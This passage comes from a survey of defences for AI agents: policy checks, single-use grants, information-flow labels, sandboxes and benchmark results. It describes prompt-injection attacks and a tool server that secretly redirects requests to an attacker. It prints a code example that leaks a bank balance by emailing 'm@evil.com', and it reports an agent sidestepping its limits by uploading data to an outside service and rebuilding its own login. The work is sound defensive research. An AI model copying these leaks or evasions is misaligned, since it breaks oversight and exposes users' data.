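*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*),

that is, if the new policy allows nothing that the old one blocked. Any other change is an *expansion*, even if it removes ten permissions and adds one. An SMT solver, a program that searches for values that satisfy a logical formula, looks for a call that *P*′ would allow and *P* would not. If there is no such call, Progent applies the change automatically. If there is one, the change has to wait for approval.

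The reviewer may comment that the report is missing the August figures, which are not among the approved records. The assistant needs an expansion to open that file, just as it needs one to write to Bob. The solver flags both but can't determine whether either is justified. Only someone with authority over the August file or the list of recipients can decide that, and neither the assistant nor a document's author has that authority.

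This protection depends on the approver. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that planted text in a tool's result may lead Progent's update mechanism to relax its limits. The solver answers this objection well if the approver examines each request, because the limits then can't be relaxed unnoticed. But Progent can also approve every expansion automatically, and then the objection stands. Shi and colleagues used that setting in their main tests to simulate a careless user, so those results don't show how well the system works when someone refuses requests. They report that only 6 percent of policy updates in one set of tests needed approval, which suggests that a person could give each request some attention.

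Narrowing a policy never adds a permission, but it can still be misused. Suppose the first policy allows mail to anyone in the organisation's directory of outside contacts, and the assistant is to fill in Alice's address later. If Bob is also in the directory, a planted line may get the language model to propose a policy that permits only Bob. Progent applies this policy without asking for approval because it only narrows the first one. The mistake was making the first policy broad enough to allow mail to Bob. The guarantee that authority can only shrink is therefore most useful when the first policy permits little.

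### A grant for one action

Between the decision and the action, the reviewer may withdraw the sign-off, or the assistant may correct a figure in the text the monitor approved. Wu and colleagues address this with an *execution grant*, which is permission to carry out one exact action once.

The check begins once every detail of the action is fixed, here including the final file and Alice's address. Both policies must permit the action, and all required evidence must be valid. A sign-off doesn't count if it is missing, expired, contradicted by another record or of unknown status. The system then records the decision and everything it was based on. This record can support a grant, which the assistant must redeem to act, but the record itself gives no authority.

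When a grant is redeemed, the system rechecks the conditions and marks the grant as used in the same step. If the assistant has changed a figure, the file no longer matches the grant and needs a new decision. If the reviewer has withdrawn the sign-off, the system can revoke the grant before anyone uses it. A used, revoked or expired grant can't be reactivated, so issuing a single grant also limits the assistant to one message.

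Wu and colleagues tested this with a small program for financial transfers. In each of 100 trials, the program received 32 simultaneous attempts to redeem the same grant, and exactly one succeeded. The program stored its grants in the memory of a single system, and Wu and colleagues don't claim that it is ready for production. The scheme also can't make a mail server require a grant. If the assistant's ordinary credential is still enough to send a message, a misled assistant can send one without using the grant.

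## How are data flows and running code kept inside the boundary?

The monitor could limit the report to Alice because its rules already contained her address. Suppose the user instead says the address is in the project memo, which many people can edit, and someone has put Bob's address next to Alice's name. The assistant proposes a mail call with one recipient and one file. The call doesn't show where the address came from, and the monitor has no stored address to compare it with.

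A check on single calls also misses what a program does after the call that starts it. If the assistant is allowed to run scripts to add up sales figures, the monitor checks only the request to run a script. The script can then open files and connect to servers without making another tool call. Besides tracking where each value came from, which deals with the memo, the software has to confine the process that runs the script.

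### Labels and how they combine

Information-flow control consists of rules that follow data through a computation and limit what the data may influence and where it may go. The system attaches a label to each value. An *integrity* label records who may have influenced the value, and a *confidentiality* label records who may read it. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use both in Fides, an agent design from Microsoft. In the simplest version, a value is either trusted or untrusted, and either public or secret. More detailed labels list the people concerned. When software combines two values *x* and *y*, the result *xy* gets the label

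readers(*xy*) = readers(*x*) ∩ readers(*y*),
writers(*xy*) = writers(*x*) ∪ writers(*y*).

Only people who may read both parts may read the result, and anyone who could have influenced either part may have influenced the result.

| Value | Who may read it | Who may have influenced it |
|---|---|---|
| Sales record | User, reviewer, finance team | Finance team |
| Customer list | User, reviewer, sales team | Sales team |
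| Draft made from both | User, reviewer | Finance team, sales team |

A language model's output is hard to label because nobody can reliably tell which parts of the input shaped it. The safe rule is to give the output the combined label of everything the model has read. But under this rule, once the assistant reads the memo, all its later calls count as influenced by whoever can edit the memo. A policy that accepts only trusted calls would then stop the assistant from sending anything, including messages unrelated to the memo. CaMeL and Fides avoid this by keeping untrusted text away from the model that chooses the calls.

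### CaMeL: a plan made before reading

CaMeL is a design that Google DeepMind published in 2025. It builds on Simon Willison's proposal to divide an agent's work between two models, one that plans and one that reads. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works:

1. The *privileged model* receives the user's request, which CaMeL treats as trusted, and writes a plan as a program in a restricted form of Python.
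2. An interpreter runs the program and makes all the tool calls. Neither model calls a tool itself.
3. When the plan needs a fact from an untrusted text, the interpreter passes the text to the *quarantined model*. This model has no tools and returns a value of a specified kind, such as an email address.
4. The interpreter stores each value together with its *capabilities*, a record of where the value came from and who may read it.
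5. Before each tool call, a policy function receives the tool's name, its arguments and their capabilities. It allows or denies the call and gives a reason.

For the report, the plan might look like this, adapted from an example in *CaMeLoT*:

```
memo = read_document("project memo")
address = ask_quarantined("Find Alice's email address", memo)
report = read_document("report, version 3")
send_mail(address, report)
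```

An instruction in the memo to copy in Bob can't add a second mail call, because the privileged model finished the plan before anyone opened the memo. The memo can still change the value of `address`, so separating the two models protects the choice of steps but not the data in them. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) gives an altered recipient address as an example of an attack that CaMeL's capabilities are meant to stop. When the plan reaches its last line, the policy function can detect that the address came from the memo and deny the call.

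By then the agent has already done all the work that leads up to the mail. CaMeLoT, an extension of CaMeL, checks the plan before any tool runs. It translates the plan into a diagram of possible steps. A program called a model checker then examines every path through the diagram for rule violations. A rule might require the recipient of a mail to be trusted on every path. The plan above breaks this rule whatever the memo contains, so CaMeLoT can reject it. It then describes the offending path to the privileged model, which tries to repair the plan.

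Rules of this kind can also require something to happen, such as a security team's rule that every incident ticket must eventually be closed or passed on. CaMeL checks each call as it comes, so it has no natural way to express such a rule. Checking in advance does cause some false alarms. CaMeLoT assumes that a loop may repeat any number of times, so it can reject a safe plan. It also leaves rules about actual values to CaMeL, since those values aren't known until the program runs.

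### Fides: labels carried through the agent loop

A plan written in advance suits a task whose steps are known. It suits less well a request such as "read my last three messages and, if one asks for a meeting, put it in my calendar", where the next step depends on what the messages contain. Fides lets the model choose each step after seeing the result of the last one, but controls how much of the result it sees:

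1. A tool returns a result in which each field, such as a message's subject or body, has its own label.
2. If a field's label is more restrictive than the label of the conversation so far, Fides stores the field in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name.
3. The model chooses the next call and can use the variable's name as an argument.
4. Fides replaces the name with the stored value and its label, and checks the call against the policy.
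5. If the call passes, Fides runs it. The result gets the combined label of the call, its arguments and all the data the tool may have read.

In the report task, the planning model would never receive the memo itself. It would receive a variable name such as `memo_1`, use a separate model, which has no tools, to extract Alice's address from the memo, receive the name `address_1`, and propose an email to `address_1`. The address inside the variable would still be labeled "untrusted".

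Costa and colleagues give two basic policies. One allows a consequential call only if the call and its arguments are trusted. The other allows a message only if everyone who will receive it may read its contents:

recipients ⊆ readers(message).

The second policy keeps a message from carrying secrets to people who aren't allowed to read them, although a prompt injection can still trigger the message. A developer can also set different requirements for different arguments. For example, an email may need a trusted recipient, while its text can draw on an untrusted web page.

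To decide about the meeting, however, the planning model needs some information from the messages. If it opens the variable, the whole conversation takes on the label of the messages, and the policy may block later calls. Fides therefore lets the model query the separate reader for an answer of a fixed type, such as yes or no. A policy may accept a yes-or-no answer because it can carry only one bit of untrusted influence. If the answer is yes, the reader extracts the date and the participants into another variable, and the planning model puts that variable into the calendar call without reading its contents.

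A message can still fool the model that reads it. Costa and colleagues give the example of a message that instructs the model to produce an empty summary. Fides then delivers that summary to the right person. The policy could also require the text to be trusted, but then Fides could not summarise mail from outsiders at all.

Both designs also require considerable trust. Like earlier work of this kind, including CaMeL and Fides, *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) assumes that the user, the planning model and the tools' code are trustworthy. The label policy still protects against some mistakes by the planning model because it applies to every call, whatever the reason for the call. But a tool that labels an outsider's text as trusted defeats the scheme without breaking any rule.

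### What the proofs cover

Fides guarantees *explicit secrecy*, meaning that it controls the direct copying of secret data into public places but not what somebody can infer from the agent's choices. If the assistant books a meeting room only when sales have fallen, anyone who sees the booking in the room calendar can tell that they fell, even though no figure left the records. Costa and colleagues chose this weaker guarantee because preventing such inferences would require Fides to forbid almost every publicly visible action after the agent has accessed a secret.

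CaMeL does try to control them, but Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found leaks. One of them depends on a branch of the program that doesn't run. Their example concerns an agent that manages a bank account, and an attacker who wants to know whether the balance is above some threshold. A program with this structure reveals it:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
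if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to false, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so CaMeL still treats `rich` as public and lets the email go out. If the balance is low, the fourth line sets `rich` to false and no email goes out. The attacker can therefore tell whether the balance is high by whether the email arrives.

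The other leak is in the code around the interpreter. When a plan fails, CaMeL tries again using a retry loop written in ordinary, untracked Python. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt may reveal one yes-or-no answer about it. One answer is usually tolerable, but an attacker who can cause repeated attempts could learn a balance between 0 and 1,023 euros in ten of them. CaMeL censors the error messages it passes back, which Garby and colleagues accept as an attempt to reduce the problem but not as a formal guarantee. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) criticises the interpreter for a related reason. Python programs can change the types of their values, jump elsewhere after an error and inspect themselves, which makes it hard to establish in advance where information can go.

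Garby and colleagues built LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, to close such gaps. Every value and every conversation with the model has a label. A program can split off a conversation or clear one, so a developer can separate a planning model from a reading model within the program. If a secret condition would change a public conversation, the interpreter stops the run.

The main theorem is a form of *noninterference*: hidden data must not affect what an observer can see. Take two starting situations that look the same to the observer and differ only in hidden data. Because a language model's answers are partly random, each situation leads to a range of visible results with different probabilities. Let *μ*(*q*) and *ν*(*q*) be the probabilities of result *q* in the two situations. They may add up to less than 1, since some runs stop or never finish. The theorem says there is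 a third set of probabilities *ω*, also adding up to at most 1, such that for every result *q*

*μ*(*q*) ≤ *ω*(*q*) and *ν*(*q*) ≤ *ω*(*q*).

If all runs finish, *μ* and *ν* each add up to 1, so both equal *ω* and the observer sees no difference. If some runs don't finish, the two can differ, but their statistical distance (half the sum of the absolute differences over all results) is at most the average share of unfinished runs. With 2 percent unfinished in one situation and 4 percent in the other, the distance is at most 0.03.

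The same theorem covers integrity. In this case, the hidden data are the attacker's texts and the observer sees only trusted results, so the attacker's texts can't change those results except by causing a run to stop. The theorem holds for every program in the language, including those a model writes while the agent is running. Garby and colleagues checked the proof with Lean, a program that verifies mathematical proofs, and the proof applies to the same interpreter that calls the model.

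The proof assumes that the model gives random answers that depend only on the current conversation, so it would not cover a provider whose service carried information from one conversation to another. The network connection to the model is also outside the verified code. The tests simulated the bank account and the files within the language, so with real tools the guarantee would depend on each tool labelling its results correctly.

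Tracking everything also complicates ordinary behaviour, such as correcting a plan after an error. The correction depends on the data that caused the error, so the corrected plan inherits that data's label. Garby and colleagues' test agent avoids this by trying out its plan on artificial data until the plan works, and only then running it on the real account.

### Endorsement and declassification

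Combining values only makes labels more restrictive, so without exceptions an agent would soon be unable to finish most tasks. Two deliberate exceptions prevent this. *Endorsement* allows less trusted data to influence a protected decision. *Declassification* allows restricted data to go to someone its label excludes.

If Alice's address comes from the memo, it is untrusted, because anyone with access to the memo may have changed it. Only the user and the reviewer can read the report, because it contains their organisation's records. The policy therefore blocks the mail even when the memo gives the correct address.

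| Event | Label of the address | Who may read the report | May the mail go out? |
|---|---|---|---|
| The assistant extracts the address | Untrusted | User, reviewer | No |
| The user confirms that it is Alice's address (endorsement) | Trusted | User, reviewer | No, because Alice may not read the report |
| The user releases version 3 to Alice (declassification) | Trusted | User, reviewer, Alice | Yes |

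The order matters because if the user began by releasing the report to "whoever the memo names", the last person to edit the memo would decide who gets it. Costa and colleagues link their rule on consequential calls to *robust declassification*, the principle that untrusted data must not influence a decision to release secrets.

An endorsement also needs a reason that bears on the decision. Checking that the text is a properly formed email address isn't enough, because Bob's address is properly formed too. A lookup in the organisation's trusted directory is better, and if the directory lists Alice, the assistant may as well take the address from there and ignore the memo. Another common reason is that the untrusted source can choose only from a short list. If there are four approved partner contacts, the memo's author controls two bits of information and can't add a fifth contact, but can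 still cause Alice's report to be sent to one of the other three.

Zhou and Zhang show why a short answer can still be unsafe. If the system asks a source "is this draft approved for external release?", the one-word reply decides whether confidential data leave the organisation. Limiting the form of the reply does not establish that the source has authority to approve the release.

In LLMbda, an endorsement is a visible instruction in the program, so an auditor can find every place where the program relaxes the rules. Garby and colleagues prove that endorsing a value doesn't weaken the protection of secrets. In the table, confirming the address doesn't release the report, which stays blocked until the user declassifies it. They also prove that declassifying a value need not make it trusted. Neither result shows that a particular endorsement or declassification was wise. Their test agent writes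 some endorsements into its own plans before it reads any outside data, and they acknowledge that overusing endorsements could let prompt injections through.

### Confining a running program

Labels work only for values that the tracking software handles. When the assistant runs a script, the software can track what goes in and what comes out, but not which files the script used. To be safe, it has to give the output the labels of everything the script could have read. If a script can open every file in the organisation, hardly anyone may see its output. Confining the script keeps the labels usable and limits the damage the script can do.

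The strongest common barrier is a *virtual machine*, a simulated computer with its own operating system. A container is a lighter form of isolation that shares the host machine's *kernel*, the core of its operating system, so an attacker who exploits a fault in that kernel may get out. A virtual machine has its own kernel, and processor features help isolate it from the host. A *micro-VM* is a small virtual machine that starts quickly enough for each agent to have its own.

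A program in any kind of isolation still needs some files and perhaps some connections. GitLab, a platform for software projects, publishes the rules for the sandbox around its coding agents. An agent can write only to its working directory and a folder for temporary files. It can't read the folder where developers usually keep the keys for logging in to other machines, and the sandbox protects its own settings. The sandbox also checks every network request against a list of permitted domains. Four destinations are always on the list, including the customer's own GitLab site.

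GitLab acknowledges two weaknesses. First, if the sandbox can't start, for instance because the job lacks the necessary rights, the agent runs without it by default, and the only sign is a warning in the log. Since version 19.6, administrators can make such jobs fail instead, although GitLab can't guarantee complete isolation for projects that supply their own system image. Second, an agent that takes over a service on the list of permitted domains can also use that service's connections, so each entry may give the agent access to more than one destination.

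A network filter doesn't control what an agent sends over a permitted connection. *Operationalizing CaMeL* points out that if a sandbox permits outgoing mail, a planted instruction can still make the agent send sensitive data in a plausible message. Labels on the data, or a rule about the recipient and contents, can address this. But labels don't stop a script from opening its own connection, so an agent that handles secrets and runs code needs both labels and a network filter.

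The log of the agent's actions needs separate protection, because an agent that can edit it can remove the evidence of a mistake or an attack. The organisation then bases its later decisions about the agent's autonomy on a false history. AWS compares letting an agent edit its log to letting employees edit their own audit logs. The simplest protection is to have a program outside the sandbox write the log, and to give the agent no credential that can change it.

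### Two research designs: tool servers and browsers

Agents get many of their tools through the Model Context Protocol, from separate programs called servers. Developers often install these servers on their own computers, where each one gets the same access to files and networks as the agent that starts it. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) describes a server that appears to look up places on Google Maps but contains a few lines of code that assemble an attacker's internet address from character codes. When the agent asks about a place, the request goes to that address instead. No rule about the tool's name or arguments would catch this, because the agent is making the correct call.

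AgentBound bases its approach on Android phones. Each server comes with a manifest that lists the files, networks and secrets it needs. An enforcement program called AgentBox then restricts the server to that list, so the map server could reach only Google's address. This requires no changes to the server's code and doesn't depend on the model detecting a problem.

To test whether manifests are practical, Bühler and colleagues collected the 296 most popular servers and used software to generate manifests from their source code. They sent 96 of these manifests to the servers' developers. According to the developers who replied, 80.9 percent of the manifests were correct without changes, which leaves about one in five that someone has to correct. They also said the vocabulary covered every kind of access their servers needed. AgentBox added 0.6 milliseconds on average. Someone also has to read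 the manifest of an unknown server, because a manifest generated from malicious code may list the permissions the attacker wants.

AgentBound covers attacks that reach the computer's resources, such as reading private files or running commands. Bühler and colleagues exclude attacks that only give the model false information, such as a tool that returns a false figure. If a server has permission to reach a mail service, AgentBox can't distinguish a legitimate message from a harmful one.

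*ceLLMate* (2025) presents a system that checks a browser agent's web requests instead of its clicks. For each task, the system creates a policy, ties it to a browser session that only the agent uses, and intercepts the requests in that session. It works with existing agents because it doesn't depend on how they decide where to click.

Someone still has to work out which of a site's requests count as "buy" and which count as "view". When the site changes its requests, a rule may stop matching them. The new requests are then blocked if the policy refuses requests it doesn't recognise, and may go through if it doesn't.

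### A deployed case: Azure SRE Agent

Azure SRE Agent is a Microsoft product that investigates faults in customers' cloud systems and can change those systems. In *If you want a secure AI agent, start restricting its environment*, Mehta and Agarwal (2026), two Microsoft engineers who work on the product, explain why they rebuilt it after a year in use. In the original design, the agent's control software, the code the model wrote, the tools and the credentials all shared one machine. In one test, the agent couldn't read a screenshot, so it uploaded the image to a free online text-recognition service. In another, it read the source code of its own control software and rebuilt the login procedure it found there.

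In the new design, the reasoning and the control software run in one place, and the tools and model-written code run in a micro-VM dedicated to a single agent. The two sides communicate through a narrow set of structured requests. Inside the micro-VM, the agent can inspect files and start programs freely, but it can't reach the software that sets its policy, because that software is on a separate file system. Mehta and Agarwal chose micro-VMs over containers to avoid a shared kernel. According to Microsoft's *security overview*, each tool call starts a new process, and the system ends that process and everything it started when the call is over.

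The layers are at different stages, by Microsoft's own account in August 2026:

| Layer | What Microsoft describes | Stage |
|---|---|---|
| Running code | A micro-VM for each agent, with outgoing connections refused unless a rule allows them | In use |
| Credentials | A proxy outside the micro-VM adds them to approved requests | In use |
| Secrets in tool results | Software removes recognised secrets before the model reads the result | Internal pilot |
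| Changes to live systems | Reading needs no approval, writing waits for a person, and the system blocks deletion | In use |
| Approval by risk | A separate guard judges the operation, its target and the evidence, and lets low-risk changes through | Unfinished |
| Shared use | The role of the person asking determines which tools, memory and resources the agent gets | Described as in use |

Microsoft is describing its own product here, and the post gives no test results. Microsoft's documentation also differs from the post in ways a customer should check. Mehta and Agarwal write that the sandbox refuses outgoing connections by default. In June 2026, however, Microsoft's *network integration* guide listed "unrestricted" as the default network mode and recommended it only for short-lived development and test work. The default may have changed by August, or the two texts may refer to different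 parts of the system. In August, Microsoft's *Network Controls* guide still listed a mode that lets the agent reach any internet address.

The strictest mode sends the agent's traffic through the customer's own network, where the customer can filter and record it. According to Microsoft's *network requirements* guide, this mode covers only the sandbox, and the trusted part of the system makes its own connections from Microsoft's addresses, including those for built-in Azure tools and some tool servers. These connections don't appear in the customer's firewall log.

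The documentation and the post also disagree about approval. According to Mehta and Agarwal, a person must approve every change to a live system. The security overview describes a "review" mode that works this way and an "autonomous" mode in which the agent uses its own identity directly. The customer chooses which resources that identity can change. Since the agent sends its activity records to a monitoring service in the customer's account, the customer should exclude that service.

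Mehta and Agarwal admit to gaps they have only recently closed. In one, the system blocked an action through one tool, but the agent could still take it through another channel that the checks didn't cover. In another, a tool server could expand what it did after the customer had approved it, and the protocol provided no way to detect the change. Both gaps violate Anderson's requirement that the monitor check every action. A separate machine makes that requirement easier to meet, but someone still has to find every route an action could take.

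### AWS, Windows and Nvidia

AWS recommends fixed controls outside the agent, which it calls a "security box". Every exchange between the agent and the outside world must pass through it. In AWS's own service, agents run in micro-VMs under Firecracker, an open-source program that AWS wrote. AWS says its teams have formally verified key parts of Firecracker, meaning they proved mathematically that those parts behave as specified. A gateway between agents and tools checks calls down to individual arguments, and the agent can't reach the logs. This is AWS's description of its own product, and it includes no measurements. AWS claims that manipulating the model can't bypass the controls, but this is true only if the box covers every route between the agent and the outside world.

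Personal computers are harder to protect because the agent works next to the user's files and open programs. Microsoft released an early preview of Microsoft Execution Containers for Windows in 2026. According to Help Net Security's *Microsoft wants to keep your AI agents from going rogue* (2026), developers state what an agent may do and Windows enforces those limits. One option runs model-written code in a separate process with limited access to files and networks. Another gives the agent its own session and identity, separate from the user's desktop, clipboard and keyboard, so it can't click an approval button on that desktop. Microsoft plans to offer micro-VMs for riskier work but has not yet released them.

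Nvidia has built these containers into OpenShell, its software for running autonomous agents, so that developers can use the Windows controls with it. An agent in OpenShell on Windows depends on both Microsoft's isolation and Nvidia's software, and a fault in either could weaken the boundary. This description comes from the companies involved, and the preview is too new to show how well the combination works.

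### Programs that use the agent's output

A perfectly isolated agent would be useless, because the user wants what it produces. A program outside the sandbox eventually has to open the agent's file, run its code or read its notes. This program has its own permissions, which are often wider than the agent's. If it treats the agent's output as instructions, a misled agent can act through it without breaking out of the sandbox, which is known as the confused deputy problem.

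For example, suppose the assistant saves the report in a shared folder, and a trusted program outside the boundary converts it for mailing. If the converter runs small programs embedded in the document, anyone who controls the document can take over the converter and reach the mail server through it. If the converter only copies text and numbers into a fixed template, the worst outcome is a report with wrong text and numbers.

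Settings files are especially risky because the boundary may depend on them. GitLab, for example, keeps a project's sandbox rules in a file within the project, where a coding agent may well be working. GitLab reads the file only from the project's main version, so a change has no effect until someone merges it. This protects the sandbox if a person reviews the change or the agent can't merge, but an agent that can merge its own work without review can write the rules for its next run.

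The later program can also be the agent itself. Mehta and Agarwal describe a team's shared agent whose memory persists between sessions. A user with few rights can teach it a habit, and the agent may apply that habit to an administrator's request the next day. Microsoft's answer is to restrict writes to the shared memory by the caller's role. Similarly, any output should keep the label of its least trusted source, and the next program should have no more authority over it than the task needs.

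How well the sandbox isolates the agent thus depends on every trusted program that later acts on the agent's output. A security team can list these programs when it sets up the sandbox, but the list goes out of date as soon as someone connects a new tool to the shared folder.

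## How much do boundaries prevent in tests, and what do they cost?

Researchers run an agent on prepared tasks with and without a boundary, then compare the results to estimate how often the agent would misuse a program that acts on its output and how much legitimate work the boundary would stop. A list of those programs doesn't show either.

### How the tests work

AgentDojo, a benchmark (a standard set of test tasks) published in 2024, simulates online banking, an office workspace, travel bookings and the messaging service Slack. In some runs, a tool result contains a planted instruction, such as to reserve the most expensive hotel in Paris or invite a stranger to the company's Slack. AgentDojo measures *utility*, the share of legitimate tasks the agent completes, and the *attack success rate*, the share of planted attacks that achieve the attacker's goal. ASB, another benchmark for planted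 instructions, has ten agent scenarios and five attack templates.

τ²-bench tests whether an agent follows company rules. The agent works in customer service for an airline or a shop, a second language model plays the customer, and the rules are in the agent's instructions. No third party plants text, although some of the simulated customers lie. At the end, the benchmark compares the airline's or shop's database with the correct one, so an agent that politely cancels the wrong booking fails.

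### What the boundaries prevented

The table covers Progent, four policies run in FORGE, and a set of simple checks from *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026). Each arrow points from the result without the boundary to the result with it.

| Boundary | Paper and date | Test and agent's model | Attack success | Utility | Delay or other cost |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | Shi and colleagues, April 2025, revised 2026 | AgentDojo, four settings, GPT-4o | 39.9% → 1.0% | About the same | Extra model calls to write policies; 6% of policy updates need approval |
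| Progent | The same | ASB, ten scenarios, GPT-4o | 70.3% → 3.9% | About the same | Extra model calls to write policies |
| Fides's label policy, run in FORGE | Palumbo and colleagues, February 2026, later revised | AgentDojo, 97 ordinary and 949 attacked runs, five times, GPT-4o | 14.1% → 0.6% | 83.7% → 33.2% | 5.9 → 10.2 seconds per run |
| FORGE's own policy | The same | The same | 14.1% → 0.9% | 83.7% → 62.5% | 5.9 → 7.7 seconds per run |
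| FORGE, airline rules | The same | τ²-bench, 50 tasks, four times, average of Claude Opus 4.5, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview | No planted attacks | 74.7% → 81.5% | 67.1 → 70.7 seconds and $0.257 → $0.266 per run |
| FORGE, shop rules | The same | τ²-bench, 114 tasks, four times, same three models | No planted attacks | 86.3% → 87.4% | 63.8 → 63.6 seconds and $0.256 → $0.261 per run |
| Four gates | Reddy and colleagues, July 2026 | τ²-bench airline, 50 tasks, five times, GPT-4o mini | No planted attacks | 29.6% → 42.0% | No extra model calls for the checks |
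| Four gates | The same | The same tasks, GPT-5.2 | No planted attacks | 61.2% → 71.6% | No extra model calls for the checks |

Progent's AgentDojo row can't be compared with FORGE's, although both tests used GPT-4o. Without any defence, attacks succeeded 39.9 percent of the time in Progent's test but only 25.2 percent in FORGE's, so the set-ups must have differed. FORGE's rows start even lower, at 14.1 percent, because the figures on both sides of the arrow are for an agent that also had a simple defence, which repeats the user's request after each batch of tool results. The customer-service rows measure something different, since those tests contained no planted attacks.

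The row for Fides also measures only its label policy, not the full design. The full design hides untrusted text in variables so that the planning model can continue to work. Palumbo and colleagues applied the policy to AgentDojo's standard agent, which doesn't hide text this way, so the policy refused consequential calls as soon as the agent had read anything untrusted. The drop to 33.2 percent reflects the policy alone, and the full design may well do better.

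The comparisons within FORGE's test are fair, and one favours a much simpler safeguard, an AgentDojo filter that uses a language model to select the tools the user's request needs and removes the rest. With the repeated request, the filter allowed 3.1 percent of attacks and kept utility at 73.4 percent. FORGE's policy reduced attack success to 0.9 percent, but utility was 11 points lower. Whether the extra protection is worth the lost utility depends on what an attack could do. A firm might accept the loss for an agent that pays suppliers, but probably not for one that suggests restaurants.

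Even the 0.9 percent success rate overstates the harm that got through. AgentDojo counted 43 of the 4,745 attacked runs under FORGE's policy as successful attacks. In 33 of them, the agent attempted the Slack attack involving Fred, and AgentDojo counted the attempt even though FORGE blocked every call. In the other ten, the agent's final answer named the attacker's hotel, which requires no tool call. Only those ten attacks had an effect, a rate of 0.2 percent.

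The checks take almost no time. With 32 agents running at once on the airline tasks, the median decision took 0.19 milliseconds inside FORGE's monitor and 0.72 milliseconds measured from the agent's side. Most of the delay seems to come from what the agent does after a refusal. On AgentDojo, FORGE's policy lengthened the average run by 30 percent but the median run by only about 6 percent, so a minority of slow runs caused most of the increase. In another test by Palumbo and colleagues, agents assessing drug side effects had to obtain approval before querying a public database. FORGE reduced unapproved queries from 40 to zero over 15 runs, and all 15 answers were still correct, but the average run rose from 59.4 to 67.3 seconds because agents had to request approval and try again.

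None of the results in the table comes from a model of GPT-6 Astra's generation. The 2026 AgentDojo results still use GPT-4o, a 2024 model, and the newest models in the customer-service tests are also older than Astra. Newer models resist more attacks on their own, so a boundary has fewer left to prevent. Shi and colleagues' tests of Progent with other models give some idea of the effect. Progent reduced the share of attacks that succeeded from 6.8 to 0.5 percent for Claude Sonnet 4, and from 4.8 to 0.3 percent for Meta-SecAlign-70B, a model trained to resist injected instructions. In both cases it stopped more than nine in ten of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded, much as it did with GPT-4o, but the success rate fell by about 6 and 5 percentage points, compared with 39 for GPT-4o. Any loss of utility doesn't shrink in the same way, so a boundary that makes a resistant model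 much less useful is harder to justify unless the remaining attacks are very harmful.

### How blocking an action can complete the task

Utility rose in the customer-service rows. Reddy and colleagues set out to explain how a safeguard that only blocks actions can help an agent finish its work.

The airline's tools in τ²-bench are permissive. For example, the cancellation tool checks that a booking exists and then cancels it, even if the fare rules forbid it. The agent is supposed to apply those rules itself. If it misses one, the tool still reports success and the agent tells the customer that the booking is cancelled. For GPT-4o mini, 78 percent of the failures were silent in this way, with a wrong final database and no error message. In real use, a second attempt wouldn't fix such failures, because the airline wouldn't know that the first had gone wrong.

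Reddy and colleagues added four gates, short programs that read the database before a change and block the change if it breaks a rule. The gates check whether a booking is eligible for cancellation, whether a baggage change fits the customer's allowance, whether the number of passengers would change, and whether the agent has read a record before altering it. When a gate blocks a change, the agent gets a reason and can try something else. Unlike the monitors described earlier that refuse on error, these gates let the action through if they crash.

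GPT-4o mini completed 74 of 250 runs without the gates and 105 of 250 with them, a gain of 12.4 percentage points (95 percent confidence interval 4.0 to 21.2). A repetition with 750 runs in each condition gave almost the same gain, 12.3 points. The gain is therefore unlikely to be due to chance, but the repetition used the same 50 tasks with new random seeds, so it doesn't show that the gates would help with other tasks.

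If the gates caused the improvement, it should be concentrated in the tasks where they refused something. They did so in 26 of the 50 tasks, where success rose from 13.8 to 33.1 percent, or by 19.2 points before rounding. In the other 24 tasks it rose by 5.0 points, which is within the range of chance. Weighting each gain by its share of the tasks recovers the total:

(26/50 × 19.2) + (24/50 × 5.0) ≈ 12.4.

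About four-fifths of the gain therefore comes from tasks in which a gate refused something.

The agent also became more consistent. Averaged over tasks, its chance of getting the same task right five times in a row rose from 8 percent without gates to 26 percent with them. This matters to a business that gets only one attempt at each request.

In the clearest case, a customer gives false details about a booking to get it cancelled. Versions of the agent without gates handled this correctly in at most one of 16 runs, while versions with gates did so in all 16. The gate used the facts in the database instead of the customer's account. A better reminder of the rule would not have helped, because the customer had misled the model about the facts.

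GPT-5.2 gained 10.4 points, but Reddy and colleagues call this result suggestive because they did not repeat it and the confidence interval runs from 0.4 to 20.8 points. FORGE's airline test supports the result, with GPT-5.2 rising from 63.0 to 77.5 percent under a different policy and with a different model playing the customer. Palumbo and colleagues also split their 150 combinations of task and model by whether FORGE had blocked anything. In the 33 with a block, average success rose from 38.6 to 69.7 percent. In the other 117, it was 84.8 percent both with and without FORGE. Two research groups have found the same pattern, but on the same set of airline tasks.

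### Where the gates did not help

The shop's tools in τ²-bench already enforce many of the rules. If the agent tries to cancel a shipped order, for example, the tool returns an error and changes nothing. When Reddy and colleagues added gates to eight shop tasks, the number of successful runs fell from 40 to 37 out of 64, a difference that could be chance. Much of the drop came from a programming error in one gate, which refused corrected requests that the tool would have accepted. A gate that duplicates an existing check can prevent few additional errors and can introduce new ones.

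They also tried a gate on 200 entries from the Berkeley Function Calling Leaderboard, which tests whether models call tools correctly. The gate never refused anything. The success rate was 52.5 percent without it and 51.0 percent with it, again within normal variation. The models mostly failed by calling tools in the wrong order, and bad calls usually produced an error message.

Even in the airline tasks, a correct refusal didn't always lead to success. In one task, the gate repeatedly blocked the agent, which failed all five runs because it never found a permitted way to help the customer. GPT-5.2 did worse than before on three tasks in which gates intervened. Reddy and colleagues take this as a sign that gates chosen for one model may block too much for another.

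The gates also differed greatly in accuracy. Reddy and colleagues compared each refused change with the benchmark's correct solution:

| Gate | Refusals | Correct refusals | Share correct |
|---|---|---|---|
| Eligibility for cancellation | 161 | 161 | 100% |
| Reading a record before changing it | 90 | 70 | 78% |
| Baggage allowance | 42 | 2 | 5% |
| Cheapest fare class (tested but not among the four) | 18 | 15 | 83% |
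| Number of passengers | 9 | 9 | 100% |

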